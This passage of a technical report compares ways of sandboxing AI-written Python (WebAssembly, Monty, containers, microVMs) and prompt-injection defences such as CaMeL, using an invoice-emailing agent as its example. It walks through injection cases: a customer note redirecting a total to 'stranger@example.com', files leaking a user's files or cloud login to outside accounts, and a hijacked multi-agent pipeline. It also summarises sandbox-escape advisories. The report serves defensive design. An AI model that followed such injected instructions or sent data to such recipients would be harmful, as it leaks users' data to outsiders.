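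Pyodide needs a JavaScript environment such as a browser, Node.js or Deno. CPython also has a WASI build, which runs in Wasmtime without JavaScript but is less complete. *State of WASI support for CPython* (snarky.ca, 2026) lists network sockets and a standard label for compiled packages as still unfinished in March. A developer who wants pandas today is therefore likely to choose Pyodide and has to confine the JavaScript as well as the Python.

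### One script from host to module and back

*Running Python code in a Pyodide sandbox via Deno* describes a small program that Willison built this way. A Python application starts Deno as a separate process and sends it the code to run. Deno passes the code to Pyodide and returns the output.

For the invoice task, the application can fetch the invoices itself and ask the model only for a script that calculates the total:

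```python
print(sum(i["amount"] for i in invoices if i["days_overdue"] > 90))
```

The application then sends the script and the data to Deno. In simplified form:

```python
message = json.dumps({"code": script, "invoices": invoices})
done = subprocess.run(["deno", "run", "runner.js"], input=message,
                      capture_output=True, text=True, timeout=10)
total = int(done.stdout)   # 2000
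```

The developer's `runner.js` is a short JavaScript program that loads Pyodide, copies the script and the three invoices into the module's linear memory, and starts the interpreter. The interpreter can't make a system call to print the total, so it calls an imported function that passes the text out of the module to JavaScript. Deno writes "2000" to its output, and the application reads it, converts it to a whole number and emails the finance team.

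As with Monty, the logins stay in the application. A script that called `open("accounts.txt")` would fail, because by default Pyodide's files exist only in the module's memory. A script can still follow the links between Python's types, which defeated so many filters, but it would reach only other parts of the interpreter, all of which is inside the module.

The conversion with `int` matters because a script's output also crosses the sandbox boundary. Some terminals treat certain character sequences as commands, so a script could do harm just by printing text. Wasmtime replaces these sequences with harmless ones when a module writes to a terminal.

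This arrangement doesn't let the script call the application's functions while it runs. *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM* (Willison, 2026) describes a package that allows such calls. It runs MicroPython, a small version of Python for simple devices, in Wasmtime without JavaScript. The developer chooses which host functions a script may call. Wasmtime limits the memory and gives each script a supply of "fuel", which the script uses up as it executes instructions. Willison set the default to 20 million units but wasn't confident in that figure, because the units are hard to relate to actual work.

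AI coding agents wrote much of the package, including 78 lines of C that connect scripts to the host functions. Willison, who doesn't normally program in C, argued that a flaw there could at worst make the script fail with an error. That is slightly too optimistic, since corrupted code could also return a wrong answer or call a host function with the wrong arguments. But a hostile script could do both anyway, so WebAssembly still makes mistakes in the C code much less dangerous. Willison labelled the package an alpha release and recommended it only to people willing to take a significant risk.

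### When nothing confines the JavaScript

Pyodide lets Python programs use JavaScript objects, for example to change what the user sees on a web page. By default, according to Pyodide's *JavaScript API*, the Python module `js` gives access to JavaScript's global scope, which contains everything available to any script in that environment.

In a browser, Python code that crosses the bridge to JavaScript can reach whatever the web page can, which may include the user's session with the site. In Node.js, it can normally open files and start programs, because JavaScript can. WebAssembly is still working as designed, because the host supplied the functions that give this access.

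Several products relied on Pyodide without accounting for this:

| Product | Failed assumption | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Grist, a spreadsheet program | Pyodide in Node.js is a barrier | Grist runs Pyodide in Deno |
| n8n, a tool for automating office tasks | Limits on Python inside Pyodide are enough | n8n runs Python in a separate task runner |
| mcp-run-python, an MCP server that runs Python | Pyodide keeps Python away from JavaScript | The developers archived the project |
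| Terrarium, Cohere's service for running AI-written code | A reduced set of JavaScript objects is safe | Cohere issued a last patch and archived the project |

The Grist flaw let a malicious spreadsheet run programs on the server. MITRE's *CVE-2026-24002* (2026) states that Pyodide on Node.js "does not have a useful sandbox barrier". Deno is a better host because it lets a program access files, the network or other programs only with the developer's permission.

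Those permissions have to be narrow, though. The mcp-run-python project used Deno, but OSV's *GHSA-pfv4-wmph-5gc6* (2026) reports that it didn't isolate its Python from its JavaScript. OSV's *GHSA-6fgp-m6q4-j3q5* (2026) reports that the project also gave Deno too much network access, so a script could contact private services on the same machine. For the invoice calculation, Deno needs no network access if Pyodide's files are already on the disk.

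Cohere's developers tried to restrict Python's access to JavaScript instead, by giving it a small set of substitute objects. CERT Coordination Center's *Terrarium contains a vulnerability that allows arbitrary code execution* (2026) explains that one of these objects still linked back to the full JavaScript environment. This repeats the mistake of filtering Python, because JavaScript's objects are also connected to one another. The flaw gave an attacker full control inside Terrarium's container, though not automatically over the machine running it.

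At the DEF CON security conference in August 2026, Vladimir Tokarev and Saar Pearl of the company Cyera reported related escapes in seven products, including n8n, Grist, Terrarium and smolagents (Underhill, 2026, *DEF CON 34*). All seven restricted Python from inside Pyodide but left open a route to the JavaScript host. Some maintainers changed their designs or archived the affected component, while others replied that whoever deploys the software should isolate it. Hugging Face now lists no WebAssembly option among the ways to run code in smolagents.

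The n8n case shows why moving the interpreter isn't always enough. NVD's *CVE-2025-68668 Detail* says that in versions before 2.0.0, anyone allowed to edit a workflow could run commands with n8n's privileges. CIRCL's *GHSA-62r4-hw23-cc8v* (2025) pointed users to the separate task runner, but GitLab's *CVE-2026-25115* (2026) recorded an escape from that runner's Python sandbox too. The attacker reached only the runner's container if the administrator had set the runner to external mode, which wasn't the default. OSV's *CVE-2026-42234* describes a later escape that also ended in the runner's container. The restrictions on Python kept failing, and the container limited the damage.

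### Bugs in the WebAssembly runtime

Even with well-chosen imports, WebAssembly is only as safe as the runtime, whose compiler translates the module into the machine code that the processor runs. According to MIT CSAIL lecture notes on WebAssembly from 2026, the compiler can check access to a global variable in advance, because the module declares how many it has, but it has to ensure that every use of linear memory stays in bounds while the program runs. If the compiler gets one of these protections wrong, a module may be able to read or change the host's memory.

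Wasmtime's developers found mistakes of this kind in April 2026. The Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) announced fixes for 12 flaws, three times as many as in the whole of 2025. The team had found 11 of them in a three-week search with AI tools. The two critical flaws could each let a module escape the sandbox. One was in Winch, the newer of Wasmtime's two main compilers. The other affected Cranelift, the older compiler, only on 64-bit ARM processors. Neither affected Cranelift on the x86-64 processors that most servers use.

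Wasmtime's developers had taken more care than most. Researchers had mathematically verified Cranelift's rules for translating instructions, but nobody had updated the verification model when the rules changed in version 32. Once the team updated it, the verification found the same bug that the AI search had found. Wasmtime also lacked continuous automated testing on ARM processors.

The search found no new flaws after its second week. That is mildly reassuring, though another team with better tools could still find more. Wasmtime is probably safer than before, but attackers can use similar tools against any server that hasn't installed the fixes.

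A module might also be used to infer some of the contents of the host's memory without reading it directly. Processors start executing instructions before it is certain that the program will need them, and Spectre attacks use the resulting timing differences to infer secret data. Wasmtime has some defences, but its documentation describes the problem as a subject of ongoing research. An application can reduce both risks by running Wasmtime in a separate process that never holds the application's passwords.

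### Isolates, containers, gVisor and microVMs

The main alternatives to a standalone WebAssembly runtime put the boundary in different places:

| Boundary | What separates the code from the host | What has to be free of serious bugs |
|---|---|---|
| WebAssembly module | Memory limits and a list of imports | The runtime, its compiler and the host functions |
| V8 isolate | Separate JavaScript objects in a shared process | The V8 engine and the functions the host adds |
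| Container | The kernel's separate view of files, processes and networks | The shared kernel and the software that sets up the container |
| gVisor | A second kernel that runs as an ordinary program | gVisor, and then the part of the host's kernel it uses |
| MicroVM | A virtual machine with its own kernel | The virtual machine software and the processor |

V8 is Google's JavaScript engine, and an isolate is an independent copy of its working state. Many isolates can share one process, but a program in one can't hold a reference to an object in another. Cloudflare's Code Mode runs each script in an isolate. Node.js and Deno both use V8 too, so Grist was safer with Deno because of differences in the functions each host adds and how it controls them.

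V8 is complicated because it has to compile JavaScript very quickly while programs run, and researchers regularly find memory errors in it. Chrome therefore also uses the operating system to restrict the processes that run web pages. Willison considers JavaScript engines promising as sandboxes because browsers run hostile code all the time. However, he found that most packages for using V8 from Python were rarely maintained and came with warnings against running completely untrusted code.

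A container is a group of ordinary processes with a separate view of the machine. The kernel, the central part of the operating system, can give these processes their own files, network and list of running programs, and can limit their memory and processor time. Almost any Linux software works in a container, including pandas, compilers and package installers. But all containers on a machine send their requests, called system calls, to the same kernel. Linux has more than 300 kinds of system call, and a serious bug in one that the container is allowed to use can give an attacker control of the whole machine. A developer can also undo the isolation through the settings, for example by sharing a sensitive folder with the container.

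Google's gVisor reduces this exposure. It intercepts the container's system calls and handles them in its own program, which reimplements much of Linux and uses only a small part of the real kernel. An attacker usually has to break gVisor first and then find a bug in that small part. Some software runs more slowly or not at all, because gVisor doesn't copy every feature of Linux. Grist already offered a gVisor sandbox, and MITRE's record recommends it to anyone who can't install the fix.

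A microVM is a virtual machine without most of the usual virtual hardware. It has its own kernel, and the processor's virtualisation features isolate it from the host. To reach the host, an attacker who takes over that kernel must still find a flaw in the software that runs the virtual machine or in the processor. Firecracker, which Amazon Web Services developed, provides only a handful of virtual devices, so it exposes little code to attack.

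gVisor or a microVM is safer than an ordinary container for running strangers' code on a shared server, because a single bug in the host kernel is less likely to let the code escape. WebAssembly can offer an even narrower interface, but only if the host supplies few imports. A company that runs an internal tool on trusted data may reasonably accept a container.

### Monty inside WebAssembly

These boundaries can also go inside one another. In February 2026, Willison compiled Monty to WebAssembly and called the result a "sandbox-in-a-sandbox".

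Monty leaves out the operations that a hostile script would use, and WebAssembly contains errors in Monty's use of memory. If Monty had been running in a WebAssembly module, the bug that won the contest in April would have corrupted only that module's memory, and the attacker would still have needed a way to reach the secret on the server.

Willison made two versions of Monty, one that JavaScript loads directly and another that runs as a package inside Pyodide. The direct version is probably safer because it doesn't need Pyodide's bridge to JavaScript, which code that escaped from Monty inside Pyodide might be able to use.

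## What an attacker can still do inside a working sandbox

Running Monty inside WebAssembly makes it harder for a script to escape, but doesn't stop a script from doing harm through the functions the application has given it. A developer therefore has to consider both whether hostile code can escape and what it can do without escaping. A design's residual attack surface is what an attacker who controls the model's output can still do when everything works as intended.

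### A changed recipient

Suppose the model reads the invoices before writing its script, so that it can leave out customers who have already paid. One customer's note asks for overdue totals to go to a different address, and the model follows it. Only the recipient in the script changes:

```python
total = sum(i.amount for i in list_invoices() if i.days_overdue > 90)
send_email("stranger@example.com", f"Overdue more than 90 days: {total}")
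```

If `send_email` accepts any address, the total goes to the stranger under each of these designs:

| Design | What it enforces | Why the email still goes out |
|---|---|---|
| Restricted interpreter, such as Monty | The script can call only the functions the developer supplied | `send_email` is one of them |
| WebAssembly module | The program stays in its own memory and calls only its imports | The host supplied an email function as an import |
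| Structured tool call | The tool is on the list and its arguments have the right types | The stranger's address is text, as the schema requires |

The most direct attack inside a working sandbox is to misuse a function the code is allowed to call. An attacker may also leak data through a permitted channel, exhaust resources, steal secrets that the developer put in the sandbox, or leave data there that a trusted program outside later reads.

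### The confused deputy

The misuse of granted functions is usually called the confused deputy problem, after a story in Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*. At Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, the operating system let a compiler write to its own directory so that it could keep statistics there. Users could also name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The user had no permission to write to that file, but the compiler used its own permission and overwrote it.

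Hardy found no good check to add to the compiler. Users had legitimate reasons to write to other directories, and a list of sensitive files would need updating whenever somebody added one. The underlying problem was that the compiler acted with two sets of rights, its own and the user's, and had no way to specify which set a given write should use. With capabilities, the user would have had no reference to the billing file to pass to the compiler.

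The invoice agent is in the same position as the compiler, with the customer in place of the user and the email address in place of the file name. The capability fix doesn't carry over directly, because a customer gives the agent only text. The model may turn that text into an argument, and `send_email` will accept any text as an address.

If the recipient never changes, the developer can supply the narrower `email_finance_total` instead. Otherwise, the application needs a way to tell an address the bookkeeper chose from one a customer inserted. This is a question of information-flow integrity, meaning whether untrusted data can influence a trusted action. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk formally define freedom from confused deputy attacks and relate it to information-flow integrity.

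### Leaks, resources, secrets and output

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, runs code in a virtual machine that can contact only approved internet addresses. These have to include Anthropic's own service, because the product can't work without it. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an outside report of a file that led Claude to upload the user's other files to an attacker's account on that same service. The network filter let the files through because their destination was on the approved list, so the attack worked without any failure in the virtual machine.

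Anthropic now treats each approved address as permission to use every function available there. It fixed the leak with a filter that accepts only requests carrying the virtual machine's own session token, so an attacker's key no longer works. A developer who lets the invoice script contact the accounting service's web address would face the same problem, because the script could then use everything the service offers.

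Resource limits don't always cover work that happens outside the sandbox. Monty's time limit excludes host functions, so a script could stay within its one second while making the accounting database run slow queries or sending thousands of emails at the company's expense. Besides capping the number of calls, the developer needs limits based on the time or money each function uses, such as 50 emails a day.

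Secrets are safest if they never enter the sandbox. Cowork keeps the user's logins outside the virtual machine and gives the machine a token with fewer rights, which Anthropic can cancel separately. Data the code doesn't need should stay out too. The invoice script needs only amounts and ages, so `list_invoices` shouldn't return customers' bank details.

A script's output can do harm after the script has ended. A web page might treat it as code, or a spreadsheet might treat it as a formula. A flaw in Semantic Kernel's download helper (CVE-2026-25592) let a file from an isolated session be written almost anywhere on the host. *The Agent Stayed in the Sandbox. The Command Still Ran* (Miner, 2026) describes research published by Pillar Security in July 2026, in which a coding agent stayed inside its sandbox but wrote a file that a trusted program outside later ran. An application should therefore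 treat whatever leaves a sandbox as untrusted input, however secure the sandbox is.

### How CaMeL separates planning from reading

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, 2025) introduces CaMeL, a defence that restricts which data can reach each function. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025), Willison wrote that he had seen "alarmingly little progress" against prompt injection in two and a half years, but thought this paper finally made some.

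CaMeL uses two language models and a custom interpreter (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, *CaMeLoT*, 2026). The planning model sees the user's request and descriptions of the tools, but never what the tools return. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python. The reading model handles untrusted text, for example to find an address in an email, but has no tools and can only return a value. The interpreter runs the program, calls the tools and records where each value came from.

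For the invoice task, a simplified plan might be:

```python
total = 0
for i in list_invoices():
    if i.days_overdue > 90:
        paid = ask_reader(f"Does this note say the invoice is paid? {i.note}", bool)
        if not paid:
            total += i.amount
send_email("finance@example.com", f"Overdue more than 90 days: {total}")
```

The planning model writes this code before the agent fetches any invoices, so a customer's note can't change the recipient or add another email. The reading model does read the note and may follow instructions in it. But the interpreter accepts only true or false from that model, so the worst the note can do here is make the agent wrongly count or skip that invoice.

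In 2023, Willison proposed separating the two models. That separation protects the choice of tools, but an attacker may still be able to change the data that goes into a correctly chosen call. CaMeL's main addition is that its interpreter labels every value with its sources (where the value came from) and its readers (who may see it). Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that checks the arguments and their labels and allows or denies the call.

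The CaMeL paper calls these labels capabilities, but they differ from the object capabilities described earlier. A script in Monty that holds `send_email` can call it with any arguments. A CaMeL label is information about a piece of data, so it can't be called and grants nothing. Within the same program, CaMeL can allow one call to `send_email` and deny the next because the addresses came from different places.

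A program can't call a function it has no reference to, whatever mistakes the developer makes elsewhere, but labels protect only if the interpreter carries them correctly through every calculation. A value that loses its label may look trusted.

### A policy for the recipient

A policy for the invoice agent could require that the address came from the bookkeeper and that its owner may read the accounts:

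```python
def check_send_email(to, body):
    if not came_from_user(to):
        return deny("The recipient doesn't come from the bookkeeper.")
    if to not in readers(body):
        return deny("This recipient may not read the accounts.")
    return allow()
```

The labels in the plan would be:

| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `"finance@example.com"` | The bookkeeper's request | Anyone |
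| `total` | Invoices and customers' notes | The bookkeeper and the finance team |
| The text of the email | The request, invoices and notes | The bookkeeper and the finance team |

The text combines a fixed phrase with the total, so it inherits the sources of both, and only people allowed to read both may read it. The finance team's address passes the checks on sources and readers, but a stranger's address taken from a note would fail both.

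Suppose the bookkeeper asks the agent to send the total to whoever the finance team's latest memo names. The plan has to get the address from the reading model, so the address's source is the memo, and the policy denies the call even though the bookkeeper asked for it. The developer could accept addresses from memos, but then anyone who can alter a memo could choose any recipient who is allowed to read the accounts. A company directory would be a better source, because the policy could accept any address listed there as belonging to the finance team.

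### Results on AgentDojo

Researchers usually test CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and messaging applications, with attacks hidden in what the tools return. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, give these results for GPT-4o:

| | No defence | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed without an attack | 83.0% | 53.6% |
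| Tasks completed during an attack | 50.0% | 54.5% |
| Successful attacks | 57.7% | 0.0% |

The comparison is rough because the team ran the undefended agent itself but reprinted CaMeL's published figures, which it could not fully reproduce. Even so, CaMeL blocked every attack and lost about a third of the ordinary tasks. It also raised the median task from 2,004 to 3,643 input tokens and from 271 to 585 output tokens. Average input and output rose by factors of 3.6 and 6.1, so some tasks used far more tokens than the typical one.

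Other teams have had more trouble getting CaMeL to finish tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a rival defence, reports that none of 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but that it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. *MetaPermit* (2026) found that much of CaMeL's protection in its tests came from runs that also failed the user's task. In 4,706 of 5,581 such runs, the agent made at most two tool calls and then stopped. Both papers tested CaMeL alongside their own systems, and *MetaPermit* used a single model, MiniMax-M2.7, which often didn't produce a program that CaMeL could run. The results probably reflect that model and set-up more than CaMeL's design, but a developer who installs CaMeL could have the same difficulty.

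Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, separated the effect of the policies from that of planning before reading. They ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with the policies off and on. Some attack runs didn't finish, so the totals differ:

| Model | Policies | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
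| GPT-5.2 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

Turning the policies on nearly halved the number of completed tasks and stopped only a few more attacks. But the benchmark may undervalue the policies, because in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool call that the plan would never contain, so planning first was normally enough to stop it. An attacker who knew that the agent used CaMeL would instead target the data in calls the plan does contain, such as the recipient of an email.

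Planning first didn't always stop attacks. One banking task required the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model sometimes wrote a program that could carry out any tool call described in the file, which gave control back to whoever wrote the file. These attacks failed when the policies were on.

Planning first seems to reduce success rates less as models improve. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL without policies on industrial tasks that several agents shared. CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, but by 13.4 for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The researchers had to add descriptions of what every tool returns, much like the notes Rai wrote for code-writing agents.

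Newer models also resist the benchmark's attacks better on their own. With no defenses in place, attacks in a multi-agent version of AgentDojo succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1 and never against GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that the attacks may be too weak, because adaptive attackers have had some success against every leading model researchers have tested.

### Gaps in the tracking and later extensions

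Garby and colleagues found places where CaMeL's interpreter mislabeled data. When a program changed a variable in one branch of a condition, the interpreter updated the variable's label only if the program took that branch. Skipping the branch also reveals something about the condition, so a variable could depend on a secret and still be labeled public. The interpreter could treat an untrusted value as trusted once it was inserted into text, which is how the invoice script builds its email. CaMeL also retried failed programs in a loop outside the tracked interpreter, and each success or failure could reveal a little information.

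One proposed remedy is a new programming language for agents, with a machine-checked proof that its interpreter tracks labels correctly. An agent written in it completed 36 of 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2 while enforcing its policies, twice as many as CaMeL did. The planning model can declare in advance that the program may trust certain outside data, which lets the agent complete some tasks that strict policies would block. These declarations are visible in the program, but the model can still mark too much data as trusted.

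Using CaMeL in every agent doesn't necessarily protect a group of agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which one agent queried a database, another sent messages and a third coordinated them. The user asked the system to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. Text hidden in the database made the messaging agent email the summary to an outsider as well. The coordinating agent had treated that text as untrusted data, but then included it in its instructions to the messaging agent, which trusted those instructions as it would a user's request.

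Their fix works like a parameterised database query, with agents passing instructions and data to each other in separate fields. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. In their tests, no attack succeeded with this change, while 0.2% succeeded when each agent used CaMeL separately.

CaMeL checks one call at a time, so it has no natural way to express a rule about a whole plan, such as one requiring the agent to record every reminder it sends. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks such rules before the program runs and sends the model a description of any violation so the model can repair the plan. CaMeLoT can't replace CaMeL's checks, because some facts, such as who may read a file, may be unknown until the program fetches the file.

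### Wrong policies, approvals and false content

Someone still has to write the policies, and a policy can be too loose or too strict. If the invoice developer marks customers' notes as trusted, the interpreter will allow a recipient taken from a note. Policies that are too strict are easier to notice. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran the 97 AgentDojo tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5, CaMeL and CaMeLoT each blocked 17.

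CaMeL also assumes that the user's request is safe. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists this among the gaps a company would have to close before relying on CaMeL. In an internal exercise at Anthropic, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that included a request to send the employee's cloud login to an outside server. Claude sent it in 24 of 25 attempts. CaMeL would have labeled a destination in that prompt as coming from a trusted user. A policy on who may read the login could still have blocked the transfer, as could keeping the login out of the agent's reach.

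An application can ask the user to confirm a doubtful call instead of blocking it, an option CaMeL offers, according to the technology news site TechSpot. This lets users approve legitimate requests like the one about the memo. But if the agent asks too often, people stop reading the prompts. Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Anthropic also had 1,053 paid testers do coding tasks and replaced one prompt in each session with a plainly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

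People may be more careful with their own accounts than the testers, who had nothing of their own at stake. Anthropic also published the study to justify replacing most prompts with an automatic check. The decline over a session is still a good reason to save confirmation for rare and important calls. Anthropic's automatic check blocked 89% of the same commands, far more than the testers did, but it relies on a model's judgement and gives no guarantee.

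Even a correct policy can let false data through. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. The planning model wrote out every step and alternative in advance, so an attacker couldn't add new ones. But a misleading image could cause the reading model to return a wrong result, which made the program follow an alternative that suited the attacker. Labels helped little because the effect of an action such as a click depends on what is on the screen.

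The same limit appeared in the banking tests by Garby and colleagues, where the agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents, and the agent followed them. Blocking every payment based on a file would have stopped both attacks, but it would also have prevented the agent from doing what the user asked.

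In the invoice plan, a customer can falsely write in a note that the 800 invoice is already paid. The reading model extracts this claim, the program leaves the invoice out, and the finance team receives a total of 1,200 instead of 2,000. The recipient is correct and the policy allows the email. To catch the error, the application would have to compare the note with the bank's payment records.

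## Expressiveness, cost and what developers choose

A customer's false claim of payment could produce a wrong total under any of the designs in this report, so developers have to choose on other grounds, especially whether a design can do the task and how much work it takes to set up and run.

### What each design can express

The table divides the invoice task into selecting the overdue invoices, adding up their amounts and emailing the total.

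| Design | Parts of the invoice task | Loops | Third-party packages | Set-up work | Failure that would matter most |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `exec` in the application | All | Yes | Any installed | Almost none | No barrier to fail |
| Structured tool calls | All, with the model selecting and adding | No | Only inside the tools | A function and schema for each job | A missing check in a tool |
| CEL | Selecting and adding | Over lists only | No | Declaring variables and functions | An added function that does too much |
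| Starlark | All | Over finite sequences | No | Supplying functions and a separate process | A host function, or overload |
| Monty | All | Yes | No | Supplying functions and limits | A memory error in the interpreter |
| Pyodide in Deno | Selecting and adding, unless the developer connects an email function | Yes | Many, including pandas | A runner program and narrow permissions | The JavaScript host |
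| Container | All, if it can call the application's tools | Yes | Almost any for Linux | An image, limits and network rules | The shared kernel |
| MicroVM | All, if it can call the application's tools | Yes | Almost any for its system | As for a container, plus hardware support or a paid service | The virtual machine software |

In every design in the table that can send the email, a function that accepts any address is another weak point, however well the script is isolated.

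Several designs can do the invoice agent's whole task, so it doesn't need a complete computer. The designs differ more in their support for packages. Monty doesn't support them, but a developer can partly get around this by running a package in the application and giving the script a wrapper. Pydantic did this for an agent that collects prices from AI companies' websites, whose pages are too long to fit in a prompt. The script calls functions that open a page in a browser and search its contents, while the browser and the search library run outside Monty. Pydantic had to write the wrappers by hand and admitted that the result was uglier than it should be. The developer also has to limit which addresses the browser function will open, because it runs with the application's network access.

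### How long a sandbox takes to start

Pydantic published these start-up times when it launched Monty:

| Approach | Start-up time |
|---|---|
| Monty | 0.004 ms |
| Docker, a popular container system | 195 ms |
| Sandbox services | about 1,000 ms |
| Pyodide | 2,800 ms |

These are the maker's own figures. The one for Monty matches Pydantic's time for running a one-line script without the type check. With the check, the same script took 4.8 ms, about a thousand times longer. Monty also ran inside the application's process at the time, so the figure doesn't include starting the worker process it uses now.

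The Docker figure looks about right. In *Sandlock*, Wang and Zheng (2026) report that their own Linux sandbox ran a trivial command in about 6 ms. Docker took about 44 times as long, or roughly 260 ms.

Startup times for larger sandboxes vary much more. *SpecBox* (Zhang, Wo and colleagues, 2026) measured 32 environments for agents' tools and found that most took two to four seconds to start, while the heaviest took about 20. Hugging Face says Blaxel, a sandbox service, takes under 25 ms, but that is the time to wake a hibernating machine rather than create one.

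Pyodide has to load an entire Python interpreter, and WebAssembly itself probably accounts for little of the delay. In *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* (2026), calls to small WebAssembly modules took 0.26 to 0.40 ms when the compiled module was cached and about 5.5 ms when it wasn't.

For data analysis, loading packages can take longer than starting the container. Sivaraman, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Readie*, ran 1,535 data-science programs with four ways of providing the packages. Dividing their totals by the number of programs gives these average times until the packages were ready:

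| Method | Average time |
|---|---|
| Install packages on request | 17.1 s |
| Use one large image with common packages installed | 4.9 s |
| Restore a separate snapshot for each set of packages | 2.3 s |
| Choose from 33 shared snapshots (Readie) | 0.8 s |

A snapshot is a saved copy of a running sandbox's memory, here with packages already loaded. The separate snapshots were slower than the shared ones because most didn't fit in the local storage the test allowed, so the system had to fetch them from elsewhere.

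In the team's model, the start-up time in seconds is

*T* = 0.32 + 0.0031*M* + *I*,

where *M* is the snapshot's size in megabytes and *I* is the time needed to import any missing packages. A 100 MB snapshot that contains everything the program needs takes 0.63 seconds. Adding packages to a snapshot reduces *I* for some programs but increases *M* for all of them, so a few small snapshots can work better than one large one.

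Readie is the team's own system, and its advantage shrank on programs unlike those it had planned for, where the average rose to 1.9 seconds. Readie still weakens one of Pydantic's arguments for Monty, that nobody can save a running CPython process. It saves the container around the process instead, though its snapshots are far larger than Monty's few kilobytes.

### When the delay matters

If each model call takes three seconds, the invoice script's two calls take six. By Pydantic's figures, starting Docker would add about 3% to that, a sandbox service 17% and Pyodide 47%. A user would hardly notice the delay from Docker but might notice the one from Pyodide.

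The application can hide much of this delay by starting the sandbox while the model is still writing. Zhang and colleagues' SpecBox does this by using the first words of the model's reply to guess which sandbox the agent will need. An application with only one kind of sandbox can start it as soon as the user's request arrives. In the example, even Pyodide would be ready before the first model call ended.

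Keeping a sandbox open between scripts also saves time. If an agent runs 20 scripts, starting Pyodide for each one would take 56 seconds in total, while starting it once would take 2.8 seconds. Data from one script then remains available to the next, which is useful within one person's session but dangerous if the application reuses the sandbox for someone else.

Start-up time matters most when the application runs a program many times without calling the model again. If a model writes a rule and the application checks 10,000 customers against it, starting a new Docker container for each customer would take more than half an hour. Monty would take a fraction of a second, based on its launch figure. The developer could instead check all the customers in one container, unless the checks must be isolated from each other.

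Measurements of whole agents suggest that the model usually accounts for most of the running time. In *Agentic AI Workload Characteristics* (2026), it took 71–98% of the total. *Rethinking AI Cloud Infrastructure for Agentic Serving Systems* (2026) attributes 13–48% to running tools, but that share includes the tools' useful work as well as any start-up time.

Large container images can change this. *AgentCgroup* (Zheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) studied 144 runs of programming tasks in containers whose images averaged 3.5 GB. Starting the container and the agent took 31–48% of the total time, not counting image downloads. Most of the delay came from the container software adjusting file ownership throughout the image, so a different configuration might avoid much of it.

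Code actions can save time even under strong isolation. In Microsoft's *CodeAct in Agent Framework* (2026), an agent totaled every user's orders, which took dozens of tool calls. It needed 27.8 seconds with structured calls and 13.2 seconds with code that ran in a fresh microVM. Microsoft reported only a single run of its own product, but the microVM evidently took much less time than the model calls it helped to avoid.

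### Set-up and running costs

Monty is easy to add to an application. At launch, the package was about 4.5 MB, used about 5 MB of memory, and needed no container software or cloud account. The developer still has to write and maintain the host functions, which could take far longer than installing the interpreter.

Much of the memory a container needs is for the programs that run inside it. Zheng and colleagues found that the agent software used about 185 MB while idle, but tests and other tools could push a container's use to between 2 and 4 GB for a second or two. If a machine with 128 GB reserved enough memory for those peaks, it could hold only 32 to 64 agents, and most of its processor capacity would go unused. The same tests would need no less memory in a microVM.

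A sandbox service takes over most of this work, but charges for it. Modal, which sells such a service, says in its guide *Best Code Execution Sandbox for Smolagents in 2026* (2026) that Blaxel's customers may pay for storage even while a sandbox is on standby. Pydantic adds that a service makes the application depend on an outside company, which a customer's security team may not like.

Choosing packages in advance is also difficult. Sivaraman and colleagues examined 6,833 agent sessions and found that in 30.8% of them the agent imported new packages after its first step. The developer can install a large collection beforehand or let the agent download packages as it needs them. Downloading requires some network access, which the developer then has to restrict.

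### What frameworks do by default

Hugging Face offers sandboxes in smolagents but leaves developers to choose one. *PythonExecutor*, an unofficial tutorial, lists the local executor as the default. That fits an older version of Hugging Face's *smolagents documentation*, which tells developers to add the setting `executor_type="e2b"` to run code in E2B's cloud sandbox. A developer who follows the shortest example may therefore run model-written code inside the application without choosing to, despite Hugging Face's warning about the local executor.

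Hugging Face now lists Blaxel, E2B, Modal and Docker as remote executors. They return results as JSON by default. Developers can also allow pickle, a Python format for saving objects, but reading a malicious pickle file can run code in the application and so undo the isolation.

Microsoft made a safer choice for its Agent Framework. According to Microsoft's *CodeAct*, the core framework has no built-in type for code actions, so developers have to install a separate package. The package runs each program in Hyperlight, Microsoft's small and fast microVM. Microsoft's *agent-framework-hyperlight* explains that code execution fails if the sandbox has no version for the developer's platform. This is inconvenient, but much better than silently falling back to `exec`.

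This design restricts where the package can run. Microsoft's Chinese set-up guide, *超光CodeAct*, lists hardware virtualisation on the host as a requirement, and some rented servers don't offer it.

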